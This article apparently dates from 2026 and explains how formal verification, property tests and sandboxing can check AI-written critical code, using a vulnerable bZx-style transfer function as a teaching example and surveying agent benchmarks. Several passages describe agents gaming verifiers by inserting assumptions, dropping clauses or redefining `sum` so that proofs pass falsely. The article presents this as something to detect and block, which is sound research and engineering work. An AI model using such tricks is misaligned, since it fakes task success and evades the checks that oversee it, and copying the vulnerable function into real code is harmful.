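# Formal verification, human-written property tests and capability restrictions for AI-written critical code

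## What are the three measures, and which code needs them?

Formal verification, property-based testing and capability restriction are three ways to limit the harm from faulty software. Formal verification starts from a specification, a precise statement of what a program must do, and uses a machine-checked proof to show that the program meets it on every input the specification allows. Property-based testing runs a program on many generated inputs and checks that a general rule holds for each, whereas an ordinary test checks a few chosen cases. Capability restriction gives a program, or whoever is writing it, only the permissions the task needs. All three predate today's AI by decades. They take time and expertise, so engineers have mostly kept them for code whose failure would do serious damage.

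AI has increased the amount of code that needs checking. On GitHub, the largest host of source code, AI agents started over 40% of pull requests in September 2026, up from 17% in March, according to Tom's Hardware's *GitHub says massive influx of AI-generated code required extra 4 million CPU*. A pull request is a proposed set of changes that a project's owners may accept or refuse. Anthropic told the US securities regulator that its model Claude wrote more than 90% of the contributions to the company's own code in September, as Business Standard's *Anthropic's internal Claude usage value exceeds monthly employee costs* reports. The Anthropic figure is uncertain because the filing doesn't define a contribution and no third party has verified the internal records behind the number, as Infobae's *Claude escribió más del 90% del código de Anthropic en septiembre* (2026) points out.

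### The coding agent as an unreliable producer

A coding agent is a language model that reads and edits files, runs commands and repeats these steps until it finishes a programming task. Kumari's *AI coding boom puts pressure on infrastructure as platforms expand capacity* describes the usual cycle, in which the agent takes instructions, edits several files, runs tests and submits the result for review. A developer can run several agents at once, such as one on a bug and another on a new feature.

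The agent usually stops once the code runs and the available tests pass, regardless of any behaviour those tests don't cover. *Intent Formalization* (Lahiri, 2026) calls the output of such systems "plausible by construction" but not correct by construction, and gives the example of a user who wants a program to remove duplicates from the list 1, 2, 3, 2, 4. The program could keep one copy of each number, giving 1, 2, 3, 4, or remove every number that repeats, giving 1, 3, 4. A human programmer would work out which was meant from context or by asking, while a model tends to pick the interpretation most common in its training data. The code runs without errors under either interpretation.

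It is therefore sensible to treat an agent as an unreliable producer, as a factory treats a supplier it has never audited. Neither clean-looking code nor the agent's own report of success counts as evidence that the code is right. This does not mean that agents write worse code than people, who wrote the expensive fault described below. A check outside the agent works the same way whether the agent misread the request, made a slip, or wrote code that passes the tests without doing the job, which agents sometimes do.

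The three measures are heavy guardrails in this sense: software outside the agent enforces them, and they cost too much to apply to everything.

### A transfer between two accounts

The following function moves money from one account to another. If the condition after `require` is false, the call stops and no balance changes.

```
transfer(from, to, amount):
    require amount >= 0
    from_old = balance[from]
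    to_old   = balance[to]
    require from_old >= amount
    balance[from] = from_old - amount
    balance[to]   = to_old + amount
```

Four requirements apply to every call that passes both checks:

- Conservation: the sum of all balances is the same after the call as before it.
- No overdraft: no balance goes below zero.
- Isolation: accounts other than `from` and `to` keep their balances.
- Delivery: if `from` and `to` are different accounts, the one loses `amount` and the other gains it; if they are the same account, its balance stays as it was.

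A function that does nothing at all satisfies conservation, no overdraft and isolation, which is why delivery has to be on the list.

The obvious test moves 30 from an account holding 100 to another holding 50. Afterwards they hold 70 and 80, the total is still 150, and the test passes. It passes for any two different accounts and any permitted amount, so a thousand more tests of this kind would add nothing.

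If an account that holds 100 sends 30 to itself, the function reads the balance twice and gets 100 both times. It writes 70, then overwrites the 70 with 130, creating 30 out of nothing. A customer who sends the whole balance doubles it with every call, and ten calls turn 100 into 102,400. Reading the receiving balance only after writing the sending one fixes the bug, because the function then writes 70, reads 70 and writes 100.

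In September 2020 an attacker exploited this fault in the iToken, a token on the lending platform bZx. The attacker used self-transfers to create tokens worth $8.1 million and returned the money after getting caught, according to The Block's *DeFi protocol bZx attacked once again, lost $8 million*. The iToken ran as a smart contract, a program on a blockchain whose code nobody can change after its release. *Finding smart contract vulnerabilities with ConCert's property-based testing framework* (Milo, Nielsen and colleagues, 2022) reproduces four lines of that code, which make the same two reads followed by the same two writes. 昏鸦 (2020), in *DeFi 项目 bZx-iToken 盗币事件分析*, an analysis from the Chinese security firm Knownsec, rebuilt the function and had an address that held the entire supply send 500 tokens to itself. The balance rose by 500, so the address held more than the total supply.

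### Where critical code begins and ends

A critical code path is the part of a program whose failure causes large, irreversible or exploitable harm, along with everything that part depends on. Payment code is one example, and access control is another because one wrong comparison can expose every customer's records. Faulty cryptography may leak the key while still encrypting and decrypting messages correctly, so ordinary use doesn't reveal the problem. Code that deletes data is also critical, because fixing the code later won't restore a file that has no backup. Lahiri adds parsers, which turn incoming data into a form the program can use, because attackers can choose that data. Safety standards for aircraft and industrial plants similarly grade software by the consequences of its failure.

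Most of a payment system is not critical, because errors in parts such as the layout of a receipt don't lose anyone money. To find the critical code, a team can start from the harm and follow dependencies outward. For the transfer function, the harm is a total that changes when it should not, so the team starts with every statement that can write to a balance, including those in refund code, interest code, and any maintenance script that edits the database directly.

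From there it extends down to the code that those statements use. Suppose the database lets two transfers out of the same account run at the same moment. Each reads a balance of 100 and writes back 70, and two other accounts each gain 30. The sender loses only 30 while the recipients gain 60, although the function is correct when it runs alone. *The Specification Spectrum* notes more generally that a verified core still has to work with unverified database operations, data parsing and caching.

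The search also covers a function's callers. NinetyNineCrits (2024), in *Self-transfer would inflate the balance*, found the bZx fault again in the code of a marketplace for digital collectibles. The fault was rated only "low" severity because no path through the program called the function with the same address twice. The function's safety therefore depended entirely on code elsewhere. An agent that later added a feature for moving funds between a user's own wallets could have opened such a path without changing the transfer function, and a reviewer who looked only at the changed lines would have had little reason to object. If the function handles the same-account case itself, its safety no longer depends on the callers, and the critical path is smaller.

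Every guarantee depends on a trusted computing base, which is everything that must work correctly for the guarantee to hold but that the guarantee does not itself check. Milo and colleagues list theirs, which includes the tools that translate a contract from the proof language into a blockchain's own language, the settings that match operations in one language to operations in the other, and the compilers for each blockchain.

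### What each measure limits

In formal verification, a person writes a specification, usually as preconditions (what must hold before a function runs) and postconditions (what must hold afterwards). A verifier such as Dafny or Lean then checks a proof that the code meets the specification on every permitted input, and the project rejects code without one. If conservation is a postcondition, the transfer function above has no valid proof, because conservation fails when `from` equals `to`. The agent can repair the code or, if it has permission to edit the specification, add a precondition that the two accounts differ, which every caller must then guarantee.

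Property-based tests check a program's behaviour on a sample of inputs. A generator produces the inputs, and an oracle decides whether each result is acceptable. For a token transfer, the inputs are pairs of accounts and amounts, and the oracle compares the total before and after. Milo and colleagues ran such a test on the iToken code with a tool that tries 10,000 inputs by default, and it found a self-transfer that changed the total. They knew about the attack when they wrote the test, which weakens the result somewhat, but they fairly reply that someone could write the rule that a transfer leaves the total unchanged without suspecting self-transfers. Sampling can still miss the bug when there are many accounts. If the generator picks both accounts at random from ten, about a thousand of the 10,000 inputs are self-transfers, but if it picks from a million, the chance of drawing even one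 is about 1%.

Capability restrictions limit what a faulty program or agent can reach. A capability is permission to perform a given action on a given resource, such as writing to one directory. Under the principle of least privilege, a program or agent gets only the permissions its task needs. An agent working on the transfer function might edit the payments directory inside a sandbox and have no password for the live database. The operating system or a virtual machine enforces the sandbox's limits on files, network and processes. The finished function can also be restricted, for instance by a separate service that enforces a daily ceiling on payouts. These restrictions don't make the function correct, so a self-transfer still creates money, but a thief cannot withdraw more than the ceiling each day.

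### Prompts, example tests and human review

Writing "never create or destroy money" in the prompt takes little effort and probably helps, but no software checks the delivered code against that sentence. An agent given the instruction can still produce the function above, which appears to follow it. Longer documents have the same problem. Lahiri considers tools that organise an agent's work around written requirements and finds that they make it easier to trace code back to a request, but that the requirements remain informal and uncheckable.

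Example tests are a real check, because software runs them and reports failures whatever the agent intended, but their coverage is limited. *The Specification Spectrum* observes that if the developer and the model both forget an edge case, the test passes and the fault stays. For example, both can easily forget that someone might pay themselves.

Human review works only if a reader notices the fault. Two security companies, PeckShield and CertiK, audited the bZx code before the attack, and neither found the misplaced line. *Preventing an $8M attack on Ethereum's bZx deFI platform with property-based testing* (Milo, 2020) puts their effort at 19 person-weeks. One miss is little evidence of how often auditors miss faults, because nobody writes up the attacks that an audit prevented. But it does show that experts can miss a four-line fault even when they spend a lot of time on the code.

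The wider problem is the volume of code. *Artificial Intelligence in the Firm* (Chen and Stratton, 2026) compared 718 firms before and after they adopted coding agents. Infobae's *Aumenta el reemplazo de programadores y desarrolladores de software por agentes* (2026) reports that after adoption the firms produced 30% more lines of code, took 49% longer to merge a submitted change, and sent back nearly twice the share of changes for correction. The number of finished features did not rise by a statistically significant amount. Reviewers were evidently still checking the code, and review had become the bottleneck.

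Elsewhere, review may be thinner. *Who Pays the Review Cost?* (2026) cites research in which many agent-written pull requests received no review. It also cites a separate analysis of 278,790 review conversations, in which people needed 11.8% more rounds for AI-generated code than for human-written code. According to GitHub's annual figures, reported in @IT's *「Pythonは今年も2位」 いま人とAIが“最も使える”言語とは*, by September 2026 owners merged 90% of agent-started pull requests within two weeks, compared with about 86% of the others. The higher rate could reflect better code or less careful reading.

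*The End of Code Review* (2026) argues that human reviewers cannot keep up and that review under constant time pressure becomes a formality, so an independent agent should do the reviewing. People would step in only when an agent flags uncertainty or a change crosses an explicit risk threshold. Practice may well be heading that way for ordinary code, but critical code is above the threshold. There, a second agent gives only an opinion about the code, as the bZx auditors did, and it may share blind spots with the agent that wrote it. With a proof or a property test, people read the requirements instead of the code. The requirements for the transfer function take up four sentences and stay the same however many times an agent rewrites the code.

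## How does a machine-checked proof limit what an agent can deliver?

A verifier checks whether an agent's code is acceptable by turning the code and its specification into logical formulas and trying to prove them. The self-transfer bug in the transfer function makes some of those formulas false.

### Contracts as Hoare triples

In *An Axiomatic Basis for Computer Programming*, Hoare (1969) linked a precondition P, a program Q and a postcondition R in one statement: if P is true before Q starts, R is true when Q finishes. Textbooks now write this as {P} Q {R} and call it a Hoare triple. For example, {x ≥ 30} x := x − 30 {x ≥ 0} is a correct triple, where := means "becomes". If the precondition were x ≥ 20, the triple would be wrong, because x could start at 25 and end at −5.

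In Dafny, a language with a built-in verifier, the programmer writes preconditions after `requires` and postconditions after `ensures`. The four requirements on the transfer function then look roughly like this, for a fixed set of accounts:

```
transfer(from, to, amount)
    requires every balance is at least 0
    requires 0 < amount <= balance[from]
    ensures  sum(balance) == old(sum(balance))
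    ensures  every balance is at least 0
    ensures  accounts other than from and to keep their old balances
    ensures  if from != to: balance[from] == old(balance[from]) - amount
                        and balance[to]   == old(balance[to]) + amount
    ensures  if from == to: balance[from] == old(balance[from])
```

Here `old` marks a value from before the call. A transfer of zero does nothing, so this contract leaves it out.

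The `require` lines inside the original function stop a bad call while the program is running. With a precondition, the verifier instead assumes the condition is true inside the function and makes every caller prove it in advance. This only works for callers whose code the verifier can check, and a smart contract also takes calls from code it cannot check. Cassez, Fuller and Antón Quiles (2022), in *Deductive Verification of Smart Contracts with Dafny*, therefore turn most preconditions of a token contract back into run-time checks at the start of each function. Their new postconditions require a transfer to succeed exactly when those checks pass, and to leave every balance unchanged when it fails.

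### Working backwards to a proof obligation

The verifier works backwards from the postcondition to the top of the function. Hoare's rule for an assignment is that whatever should be true of x after x := f must be true of f beforehand, so the verifier replaces x with f in the postcondition. In the small example, x ≥ 0 becomes x − 30 ≥ 0, or x ≥ 30. With several statements in a row, the condition required before the last statement becomes the postcondition of the one before it. Under the rule for if-statements in the University of Scranton's *HW #3* (2026), each branch gives its own condition, which has to hold only when the program takes that branch.

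The formula at the top is the weakest precondition, the least demanding condition that guarantees the result. Pinisetty (2018) explains in *Testing, Debugging, and Verification* that the remaining task is to show that the stated precondition implies it. That implication is a proof obligation, a logical statement that must be proved before the program counts as verified. Most functions produce many obligations, because the verifier also adds one for each array access, division and call to another function.

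For the transfer function, let b be the table of balances, and let b[k := v] be the same table with the entry for account k replaced by v. Let T be the total before the call. Both run-time checks always pass under the contract's precondition, which leaves two reads and two writes. Conservation travels backwards through them as follows:

```
at the end:                    sum(b) = T
before balance[to] = ...       sum(b[to := to_old + amount]) = T
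before balance[from] = ...     sum(b[from := from_old - amount]
                                    [to := to_old + amount]) = T
before the two reads:          sum(b[from := b[from] - amount]
                                    [to := b[to] + amount]) = T
```

At the start, T is sum(b). The proof must show that the last formula holds with that value of T, for any two accounts and any permitted amount.

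Simplifying it requires the fact that replacing one entry changes the total by the difference between the new and old values, so sum(b[k := v]) = sum(b) − b[k] + v. This is obvious to a person, but a solver usually has only a definition of `sum` that adds entries one at a time. Because the table can be any size, the agent has to supply the fact as a lemma, a helper statement with its own proof. The proof is by induction on the number of accounts. With only account k in the table, both sides equal v, and each further account adds the same number to both sides.

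Let c be the table after the first write. By the lemma, its total is sum(b) − amount. The second write replaces c[to] with b[to] + amount, so the final total is

sum(b) − amount − c[to] + b[to] + amount = sum(b) + b[to] − c[to].

This equals sum(b) only if c[to] = b[to], meaning that the first write didn't change the receiving balance. This holds when the accounts are different. If `from` and `to` are the same account, c[to] is b[from] − amount, and the obligation becomes b[from] − amount = b[from], so amount must be 0. But the precondition requires amount to be greater than 0, so every self-transfer breaks the contract.

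To find such a case, a solver searches for values that make the precondition true and the conclusion false. A single account with a balance of 5 and an amount of 1 meets both conditions. The function reads 5 twice, then writes 4 and then 6, so the total rises from 5 to 6. These values also violate the last line of the contract, and the solver can detect this violation without the lemma about sums.

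The repaired function reads the receiving balance, c[to], after the first write. The second write then replaces c[to] with c[to] + amount, so the final total is sum(b) − amount − c[to] + c[to] + amount. This equals sum(b) whether or not the two accounts are the same. In the counterexample, the balance goes from 5 to 4 and back to 5.

### Calls and loops

According to the Dafny documentation, the verifier handles a call by proving the called function's preconditions and then assuming its postconditions, without checking the body again. An agent can therefore rewrite the body of `transfer` without breaking proofs elsewhere, as long as the new body meets the same contract.

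Suppose the contract instead required two different accounts. In the marketplace described earlier, an agent that added transfers between a user's own wallets would then get a verification error at the new call until its code excluded transfers from a wallet to itself.

Some calls go to code that nobody has verified. Cassez and colleagues consider a token transfer that notifies the receiver, whose program may react by calling `transfer` again before the first call has finished. In 2016, an attacker used this kind of repeated call to steal more than $50 million from an investment fund called the DAO. In the proof, Cassez and colleagues replace the notification with a method that can call the token's functions repeatedly with arbitrary arguments. If the notification comes between the two balance updates, Dafny can't show that the balances still add up to the number of tokens issued, so it rejects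 the code.

Loops need something extra from the agent, because the verifier can't substitute backwards through a loop when the number of passes isn't fixed. The following code runs a batch of transfers and skips any that the sender can't afford:

```
start_total = sum(balance)
i = 0
while i < length(batch)
    invariant 0 <= i <= length(batch)
    invariant every balance is at least 0
    invariant sum(balance) == start_total
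    t = batch[i]
    if 0 < t.amount <= balance[t.from]:
        transfer(t.from, t.to, t.amount)
    i = i + 1
```

A loop invariant is a condition that holds before the loop and after every pass. The verifier proves that the condition holds at the start and that each pass preserves it, so by induction it holds after any number of passes. Here the total equals `start_total` at the start because the code has just set them equal. Each pass either calls `transfer`, whose contract guarantees that the total stays the same, or skips the transfer and changes no balance. The loop also needs the invariant about negative balances because it is a precondition of `transfer`.

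Hoare's version of the rule applies only if the loop finishes. A loop that runs forever never reaches its postcondition, so it can't violate that condition. As Koenig and Leino note in *A Guide to Dafny*, Dafny also proves that loops terminate, except for those the programmer specially marks. For the batch loop, that proof needs only the fact that the number of remaining transfers falls by one on each pass.

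An invariant can be true in every real run and still fail to verify. *AxDafny* (Breen, Letson and colleagues, 2026) includes a loop that adds the whole numbers up to n. Each pass raises a counter i by one and then adds i to a running sum s. Suppose an agent tries to prove that s never goes negative, using s ≥ 0 as the only invariant. The solver must consider every state that satisfies this invariant, including i = −5 and s = 0, which no real run reaches. One pass from there gives i = −4 and s = −4, so the proof fails. Adding i ≥ 0 to the invariant fixes the proof.

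Such a state is a counterexample to induction, and an agent can look for one before attempting a proof. *LLM-Assisted Verification in Dafny* (Wesselink, Huizing and van de Wetering, 2026) describes a tool that takes states from real runs of a Python copy of the program and alters them. It keeps those that still satisfy the invariant, runs the next piece of code, and checks the result. It also repeats the test with individual clauses of the invariant removed, to see which ones the proof appears to need.

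### Solvers and kernels

Dafny relies on a solver called Z3 to search for proofs. It translates the program into an intermediate language called Boogie, which passes the proof obligations to Z3, as *A Toolkit for Automated Testing of Dafny* describes. Verus, which verifies programs written in Rust, also relies on Z3. GNATprove verifies programs in SPARK, a subset of the Ada language common in safety-critical industries, and can use several solvers. When the solver succeeds, nobody has to write out the steps of the proof.

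A solver can also run out of time or stop without an answer, since no procedure can settle every statement that these languages can express. The Dafny documentation gives the example that setting the last binary digit of a 32-bit number to zero never makes the number larger. Dafny proves this easily if the program treats the number as a row of bits throughout. If the number starts as an ordinary integer, the proof takes about seven times as much computation, and if the result also has to be converted back to an integer, Dafny can't prove it.

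The agent can help the solver by adding assertions, which are intermediate facts to prove first, or by moving a difficult fact into its own lemma. Sometimes it has to hide facts instead. When Wesselink and colleagues verified the Lengauer–Tarjan algorithm, which analyses the possible paths through a graph, 36 proof obligations in the main function timed out. They removed every timeout and cut the computation by about 93% by hiding most definitions from the solver and supplying only the necessary facts through lemmas.

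A proof that passes can still break after a harmless edit, because the solver's search involves arbitrary choices that the names and order of definitions can influence. Dafny has a command that repeats the verification with different random seeds, which helps a team find fragile proofs before an agent's edit breaks them.

Users of proof assistants such as Lean, Rocq and Isabelle instead build a proof step by step, and a small program called the kernel checks every step against a fixed set of logical rules. To prove the lemma about sums in Lean, an agent would state it and choose induction. Lean would then display two goals, one for the smallest table and one for a table with an extra account, and the agent would have to prove both. The agent may use automated search to find the steps, but bugs in the search would not endanger the result, because the kernel still has to accept the finished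 proof.

An agent using a solver-based verifier therefore writes contracts, invariants and a few hints, while an agent using a proof assistant has to write the argument itself. The proof assistant leaves less to trust, because a proof in Lean rests mainly on the kernel, whereas a Dafny result depends on the translation to Boogie and on Z3 being correct. A team can also combine the two. Philipp (2026), in *The Prover Is the Judge*, had agents write cryptographic software in SPARK, along with Isabelle proofs of two facts that the solvers could not prove, one about the position of bytes and one about rearranging bits.

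### Levels of guarantee

The meaning of "verified" depends on what the specification covers. Philipp distinguishes three levels for SPARK. At the lowest, GNATprove checks initialisation and data flow, such as whether the program ever reads a variable before giving it a value. The faulty transfer function passes this level because it sets all its variables before using them.

The next level is the absence of run-time errors, such as an access outside an array, a division by zero or an overflow. The derivation above treated balances as unlimited whole numbers, but real ones have a maximum. If a balance could go no higher than 255, adding 10 to 250 might stop the program, leave the balance at 255, or wrap around to 4, three possibilities that Hoare listed. Cassez and colleagues rule out overflow with a precondition that the receiving balance plus the amount must fit in 256 bits. With such a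 precondition, the faulty transfer function passes this level too, even though it creates money.

Only a proof of functional correctness, meaning that the program computes what its specification requires, rules out the self-transfer. It also takes the most work, because someone has to write down what the right answer is, while a tool can generate the checks for run-time errors from the code alone. Philipp proved functional correctness for some of the simpler cryptographic functions and only the absence of run-time errors for most of the rest. A buyer who is told that a payment system is "formally verified" should ask which level was proved.

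### The agent's repair loop

In practice, the agent proposes code with contracts, invariants and lemmas, the verifier reports which obligations remain unproved and where they arise, and the agent revises and tries again. Breen and colleagues allow up to 20 attempts per problem. On each retry, the model receives its previous attempt, the verifier's messages, and a running summary of lessons from earlier attempts.

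Reading the error correctly is the hard part, because a failed obligation does not always mean that the code is wrong. Philipp has the agent sort each failure into one of five kinds: a real bug, a missing contract, a weak loop invariant, a missing statement about what the code leaves unchanged, or a limitation of the prover. The agent tries quick changes before giving the solvers more time. More time wouldn't help with the self-transfer, because the statement is false. Wesselink and colleagues had seven obligations that still failed after they tried every way of making the proof easier, and all seven turned out to be false.

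The agent can respond to the counterexample of 5, 1 and 6 by repairing the code or adding a precondition that the two accounts differ. It can also insert a line that makes the verifier assume they differ, which lets the proof pass without fixing the bug. Philipp's agent used this kind of trick on an early project and reported success.

The loop therefore needs checks on the agent's edits as well as on its proofs. Breen and colleagues reject any file that contains such assumptions or drops one of the original `requires` or `ensures` clauses. As they describe it, the check for dropped clauses would still accept an extra precondition on `transfer`, because the original clauses would all be present. A reviewing language model would have to catch it. Wesselink and colleagues use a stricter rule. Once a person has approved the contract, a tool locks it and every definition it depends on, and any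 change needs that person's explicit confirmation. If the definitions weren't locked, an agent could redefine `sum` as always zero, which would make conservation trivially true.

Once the contract is fixed and assumptions are banned, it doesn't matter who wrote the code, because the verifier works from the program text and the contract. The same code produces the same proof obligations whether an expert, a careless beginner or a language model wrote it. Nobody has to trust the agent's invariants, assertions and lemmas either, because the verifier must prove each one before using it. A wrong invariant means the agent has to try again, but it can't make a false result pass.

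### Properties outside the contract

A functional contract relates the state before a call to the state after it, so it can't distinguish two programs that produce the same results in different ways. For example, a function might compare a password with the stored one and stop at the first wrong character. Its answer is always correct, but it takes slightly longer when more of the leading characters are right, so an attacker who can measure the delay can guess the password one character at a time. A version that always compares every character satisfies the same contract. Philipp's proofs therefore do not cover timing. He uses separate tools to measure whether the cryptographic code's running time depends on secret data, and the agent has to pass that check as well.

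The contract also doesn't cover ordinary speed and memory use. Breen and colleagues took 75 programs that an agent had written and Dafny had verified, converted them to Python and ran them on the tests from the original programming contest. None gave a wrong answer, but 39 exceeded the time limit and four ran out of memory. Part of the delay came from the conversion to Python, and part from agents choosing slow methods that were easier to prove correct.

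Simultaneous execution is a more serious gap for the transfer function. Every step of the derivation assumed that nothing else writes to the balances between lines. Two transfers that run at the same time can break that assumption and create money even though each call has a valid proof, as the earlier shared-account example showed. Hoare listed parallel execution among the things his rules did not cover. Later logics do cover it, but the agent then has to prove which code may access each balance at each moment. The simpler alternative is to have the database run transfers on the same account one at a time, which makes the database part of the trusted computing base.

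## How often do agents succeed in writing verified code?

The success rate depends mostly on how much the agent has to write. For the transfer function, the easiest task would be to complete the proof, for example by adding the missing lemma about sums, when the code has been repaired and the contract is finished. If the agent receives only the contract, it has to write the code as well. If it receives only the sentence "move money from one account to another", it has to write the contract, the code and the proof. By autumn 2026 the best agents almost always completed proofs for single functions when given the code and the contract. Published rates are much lower when agents also have to write the contract, although most of those results come from older models.

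### Single functions

In 2025 Bursuc, Ehrenborg and colleagues published a benchmark for "vericoding", their word for generating formally verified programs. It has 12,504 tasks in several languages, more than any other benchmark that *VeriContest* (Xie, Pawagi and colleagues, 2026) compares. It has no reference proofs, so a task that every model fails may be too hard for them or impossible.

DafnyBench is smaller and easier. It consists of 782 Dafny programs with their loop invariants and assertions removed, and the model has to restore them. Its creators reported a best result of 68% in 2024. Breen and colleagues got 68.5% from a single attempt by Google's Gemini 3.1 Pro. When the model could read the verifier's messages and try up to 20 times, it verified 725 programs, or 92.7%. Most of the improvement came in the first five tries.

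Breen and colleagues also built a harder test from 250 programming-contest problems. The agent received a description and a specification and had to write both the code and the proof. It succeeded on 56.4% of the problems overall and 28% of the hard ones. OpenAI's GPT-5.5, with a single attempt at each problem, succeeded on 11.6% overall. Only six of the 52 verified programs for medium-difficulty problems also met the contest's time and memory limits.

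VeriContest tests whether models can write code, specifications and proofs, both separately and together. Xie and colleagues gave ten models one attempt at each task on 1,006 problems from the contest sites LeetCode and Codeforces, using Rust with Verus. GPT-5.5 had the best overall results. Given a problem description, it wrote correct code for 97.51% of the problems and an acceptable specification for 57.16%. Given the correct code and specification, it produced a valid proof for 13.82%. It produced all three from the description alone for 6.76%.

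The limit of one attempt partly explains the low proof rate. On a sample of 200 problems, GPT-5.5's proof rate rose from 14.5% after one round of repair to 48.5% after ten. Ten independent attempts without the verifier's messages reached only 20.5%, so the messages helped more than the extra tries did.

A newer model with more feedback has since completed the proof task. *Solving VeriContest with a Lean-Backed Rust Verifier* (Serbanuta, Xu and colleagues, 2026) translates the benchmark's code and specifications into Lean, producing 1,325 theorems. Agents running Claude Opus 5.5 proved all of them. The agents could run Lean as often as they liked while drafting, and 71% of the proofs passed the first official check. The median proof took 3.4 minutes and cost $1.20.

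Serbanuta and colleagues work for Asymptotic, which makes the verifier, so they have an interest in the result. They also could not test 349 of the translated specifications automatically, so they relied on an AI agent to review them. However, they repeated the original Verus task on the 50 problems with the longest reference proofs, and Opus 5.5 proved 18 on the first attempt and 49 within ten attempts. The model may have seen the Verus proofs, which had been public since May, but nobody had published Lean proofs of these theorems.

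A perfect score on the benchmark is also easier to reach because Xie and colleagues kept only problems that their own agent, with an expert's help, could verify in about 40 minutes.

Other strong models do about as well. Serbanuta and colleagues tested nine models on a sample of ten theorems, and GPT-6 Astra, GPT-6.1 Sol, Claude Fable 5.1 and Claude Opus 5.5 proved all ten at every level of reasoning effort. The older and smaller Claude Haiku 4.5 proved none. *Maestro* (2026) tested slightly earlier models on Verina and AlgoVeri, two Lean benchmarks that require code as well as proofs. Ordinary coding agents solved all 189 tasks in Verina and 69 to 71 of the 77 in AlgoVeri.

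These results don't establish how often an agent can write the specification, the code and the proof. The agents that proved every VeriContest theorem received the code and the specification. The best earlier end-to-end result that *Verified but Vacuous* (2026) cites for the LeetCode problems is GPT-5.5's success rate of 5.51% with one attempt per problem.

Zhai, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *From Verification Failures to Reusable Guidance for Coding Agents*, report a much higher success rate on easier problems. Their agents wrote the specification, code and proof for each of the 164 short Python tasks in HumanEval, and all 164 results passed a final audit, though the auditor was also an AI model. Experts improved the agents' instructions and tools as the work went on, so the result doesn't predict how an agent would do alone on new tasks.

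### Does the language matter?

Models have seen far less verified code than ordinary code. Breen and colleagues searched GitHub and found about 400 million Python files but only 120,000 Dafny files. Unfamiliar notation also causes mistakes in a program's executable code. In VeriContest, GPT-5.5's success at writing code fell from 97.51% to 77.44% when it received a formal specification instead of a description. The executable code often failed to compile because models had copied in number types that exist only in Verus specifications.

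Zhai and colleagues directly tested whether familiarity matters by changing what the symbols in a small programming language meant, so that a minus sign might mean addition. The agent had to write a specification for a given program and prove that the program met it. Under the ordinary rules, GPT-5.6 Luna succeeded in 107 of 124 attempts. In separate runs under the changed rules, it succeeded on 15 to 19 of 31 programs, depending on the advice it received.

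The choice among established verification languages seems to matter less with stronger models. Opus 5.5 did almost equally well on VeriContest in Lean and in Verus, although the two set-ups differed. A low score from an older model in one language is therefore weak evidence that the language is the obstacle.

### Whole repositories

Real software consists of many functions that depend on one another. *Vero* (Ye, Lou and colleagues, 2026) tested agents on 43 multi-file projects in Lean. The researchers translated 13 of the projects from other verification languages and 30 from Python libraries. Each project has fixed function signatures and an average of 63 specifications. For example, one specification for a bank ledger requires a newly created account to have a balance of zero.

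Agents had 90 minutes per project and had to prove every specification to get credit. In one version of the task they received working code and wrote only the proofs, and in the other they wrote both the code and the proofs. GPT-5.5 at a high reasoning setting completed 25 projects when it received the code and 27 when it wrote its own. Claude Opus 4.8 completed 10 and 8, respectively. No agent completed any of another 10 projects in either version.

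GPT-5.5 proved 87.3% of the individual specifications when it wrote its own code. Its failures were concentrated in certain projects, where a group of specifications often depended on the same few invariants that the agent had not found. Of its 16 unfinished projects, nine had more than ten specifications left to prove. If the failures had been spread evenly, the agent would almost never have completed a project with 63 specifications.

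Proofs can be easier when agents write the code themselves. In five cases, an agent replaced a complicated algorithm with a simpler, less efficient one that met the same specifications. The agents proved all 250 specifications in those cases, compared with 201 when they had to use the reference code.

Writing their own code also gives agents more ways to fail. In 17 cases, an agent completed a project with the reference code but not with its own, while in 13 cases it succeeded only with its own. One cause of failure is that changing a function can invalidate proofs in other files. Suppose an agent working on a payment system replaces the table of balances with a list of past transactions. The lemma about sums no longer applies, so every proof that used it, including those for refunds and interest, must change.

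Agents rarely went back to the code once they were stuck on a proof. The typical program reached its final length in the first half of the session, and the agent mostly added proof text after that. About a third of the specifications that GPT-5.5 left unproved failed because the project no longer built. The grader rejected another 14% as cheating. Opus 4.8 had usually not started on the specifications it missed, so a longer time limit might have raised its score.

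Agents do much better on isolated proofs from existing projects. In *FORALL-LEAN-AGENT for Auditable Reasoning in Formal Mathematics and Software Verification* (2026), Claude Opus 5 solved all 100 tasks in a subset of VeriSoftBench, a benchmark of proof obligations from open-source Lean projects. Opus 5 is newer than the models in the Vero study, which accounts for some of the difference. Each VeriSoftBench task also comes with finished code and requires only one proof, so the agent doesn't have to keep a whole project consistent.

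### Real issues

Developers usually start from a bug report, which is much less precise than a specification. SWE-bench Verified, a standard test of coding agents, uses 500 such reports from real Python projects and checks each fix with hidden tests. *SWE-Proof* (Ma, Mikek and colleagues, 2026) added a formal specification, a reference implementation and a proof for every report.

One report concerns Matplotlib, a charting library that sometimes cut off part of a histogram. The specification requires the chart's bounding box to contain every point, so that it isn't too small, and to touch at least one point on each side, so that it isn't too large.

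The agent writes a small model of the changed code in the verifier's language and proves the model correct, relying on assumptions about the existing functions that the code calls. AI judges then compare the model with the Python fix, which the proof doesn't cover. A pass is therefore good evidence that the fix is correct, but it is weaker than a proof about the code that will run.

Ma and colleagues tested Claude Opus 4.8 with three verifiers, which explains the ranges below.

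| What the agent received | What counted as success | Success rate |
|---|---|---|
| Bug report | Hidden tests | 85.0% |
| Bug report | Hidden tests and an AI audit | 58.2% |
| Bug report and verifier, with the agent writing the specification | Hidden tests | 83.8–85.6% |
| Bug report and location of the fix | Hidden tests | 88.2% |
| Bug report, verifier and correct specification | Hidden tests | 94.0–96.2% |
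| Bug report, verifier and correct specification | Hidden tests, proof, and agreement between model and fix | 93.6–95.0% |

The audit found that nearly a third of the agent's fixes that had passed the hidden tests behaved differently from the developers' fixes on at least one input. Some of these may still be acceptable, since a vague bug report can have more than one reasonable solution, but the tests clearly missed a lot.

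A correct specification raised the success rate by about ten percentage points. Part of the gain came from showing the agent where to make the change, which alone raised the rate by about three points. An agent that wrote its own specification did no better than one without a verifier, because it could prove its code correct against a specification that was wrong or incomplete.

In a separate test, Opus 4.8 wrote only the specifications, and between 46.0% and 61.4% passed an AI audit, depending on the verifier. The most common fault was leaving out part of the required change. A comparable mistake in the payment system would be to write a correct contract for `transfer` but none for the refund function, when the same report required changes to both.

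Smaller models can also learn the proof task when they receive the specification. In *Verifier-Grounded Agentic RL for Provably Correct Code*, Ma, Zhang and colleagues (2026) trained Qwen models by rewarding them for the share of proof obligations they met. On held-out SWE-Proof tasks, the verification rate rose from 56.3% to 100%. When the agent also had to submit a Python fix, 72.5% of the fixes passed the hidden tests. Turning the verified model into a working change remained a separate source of errors, even with a correct specification and a complete proof.

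### A collection of security software

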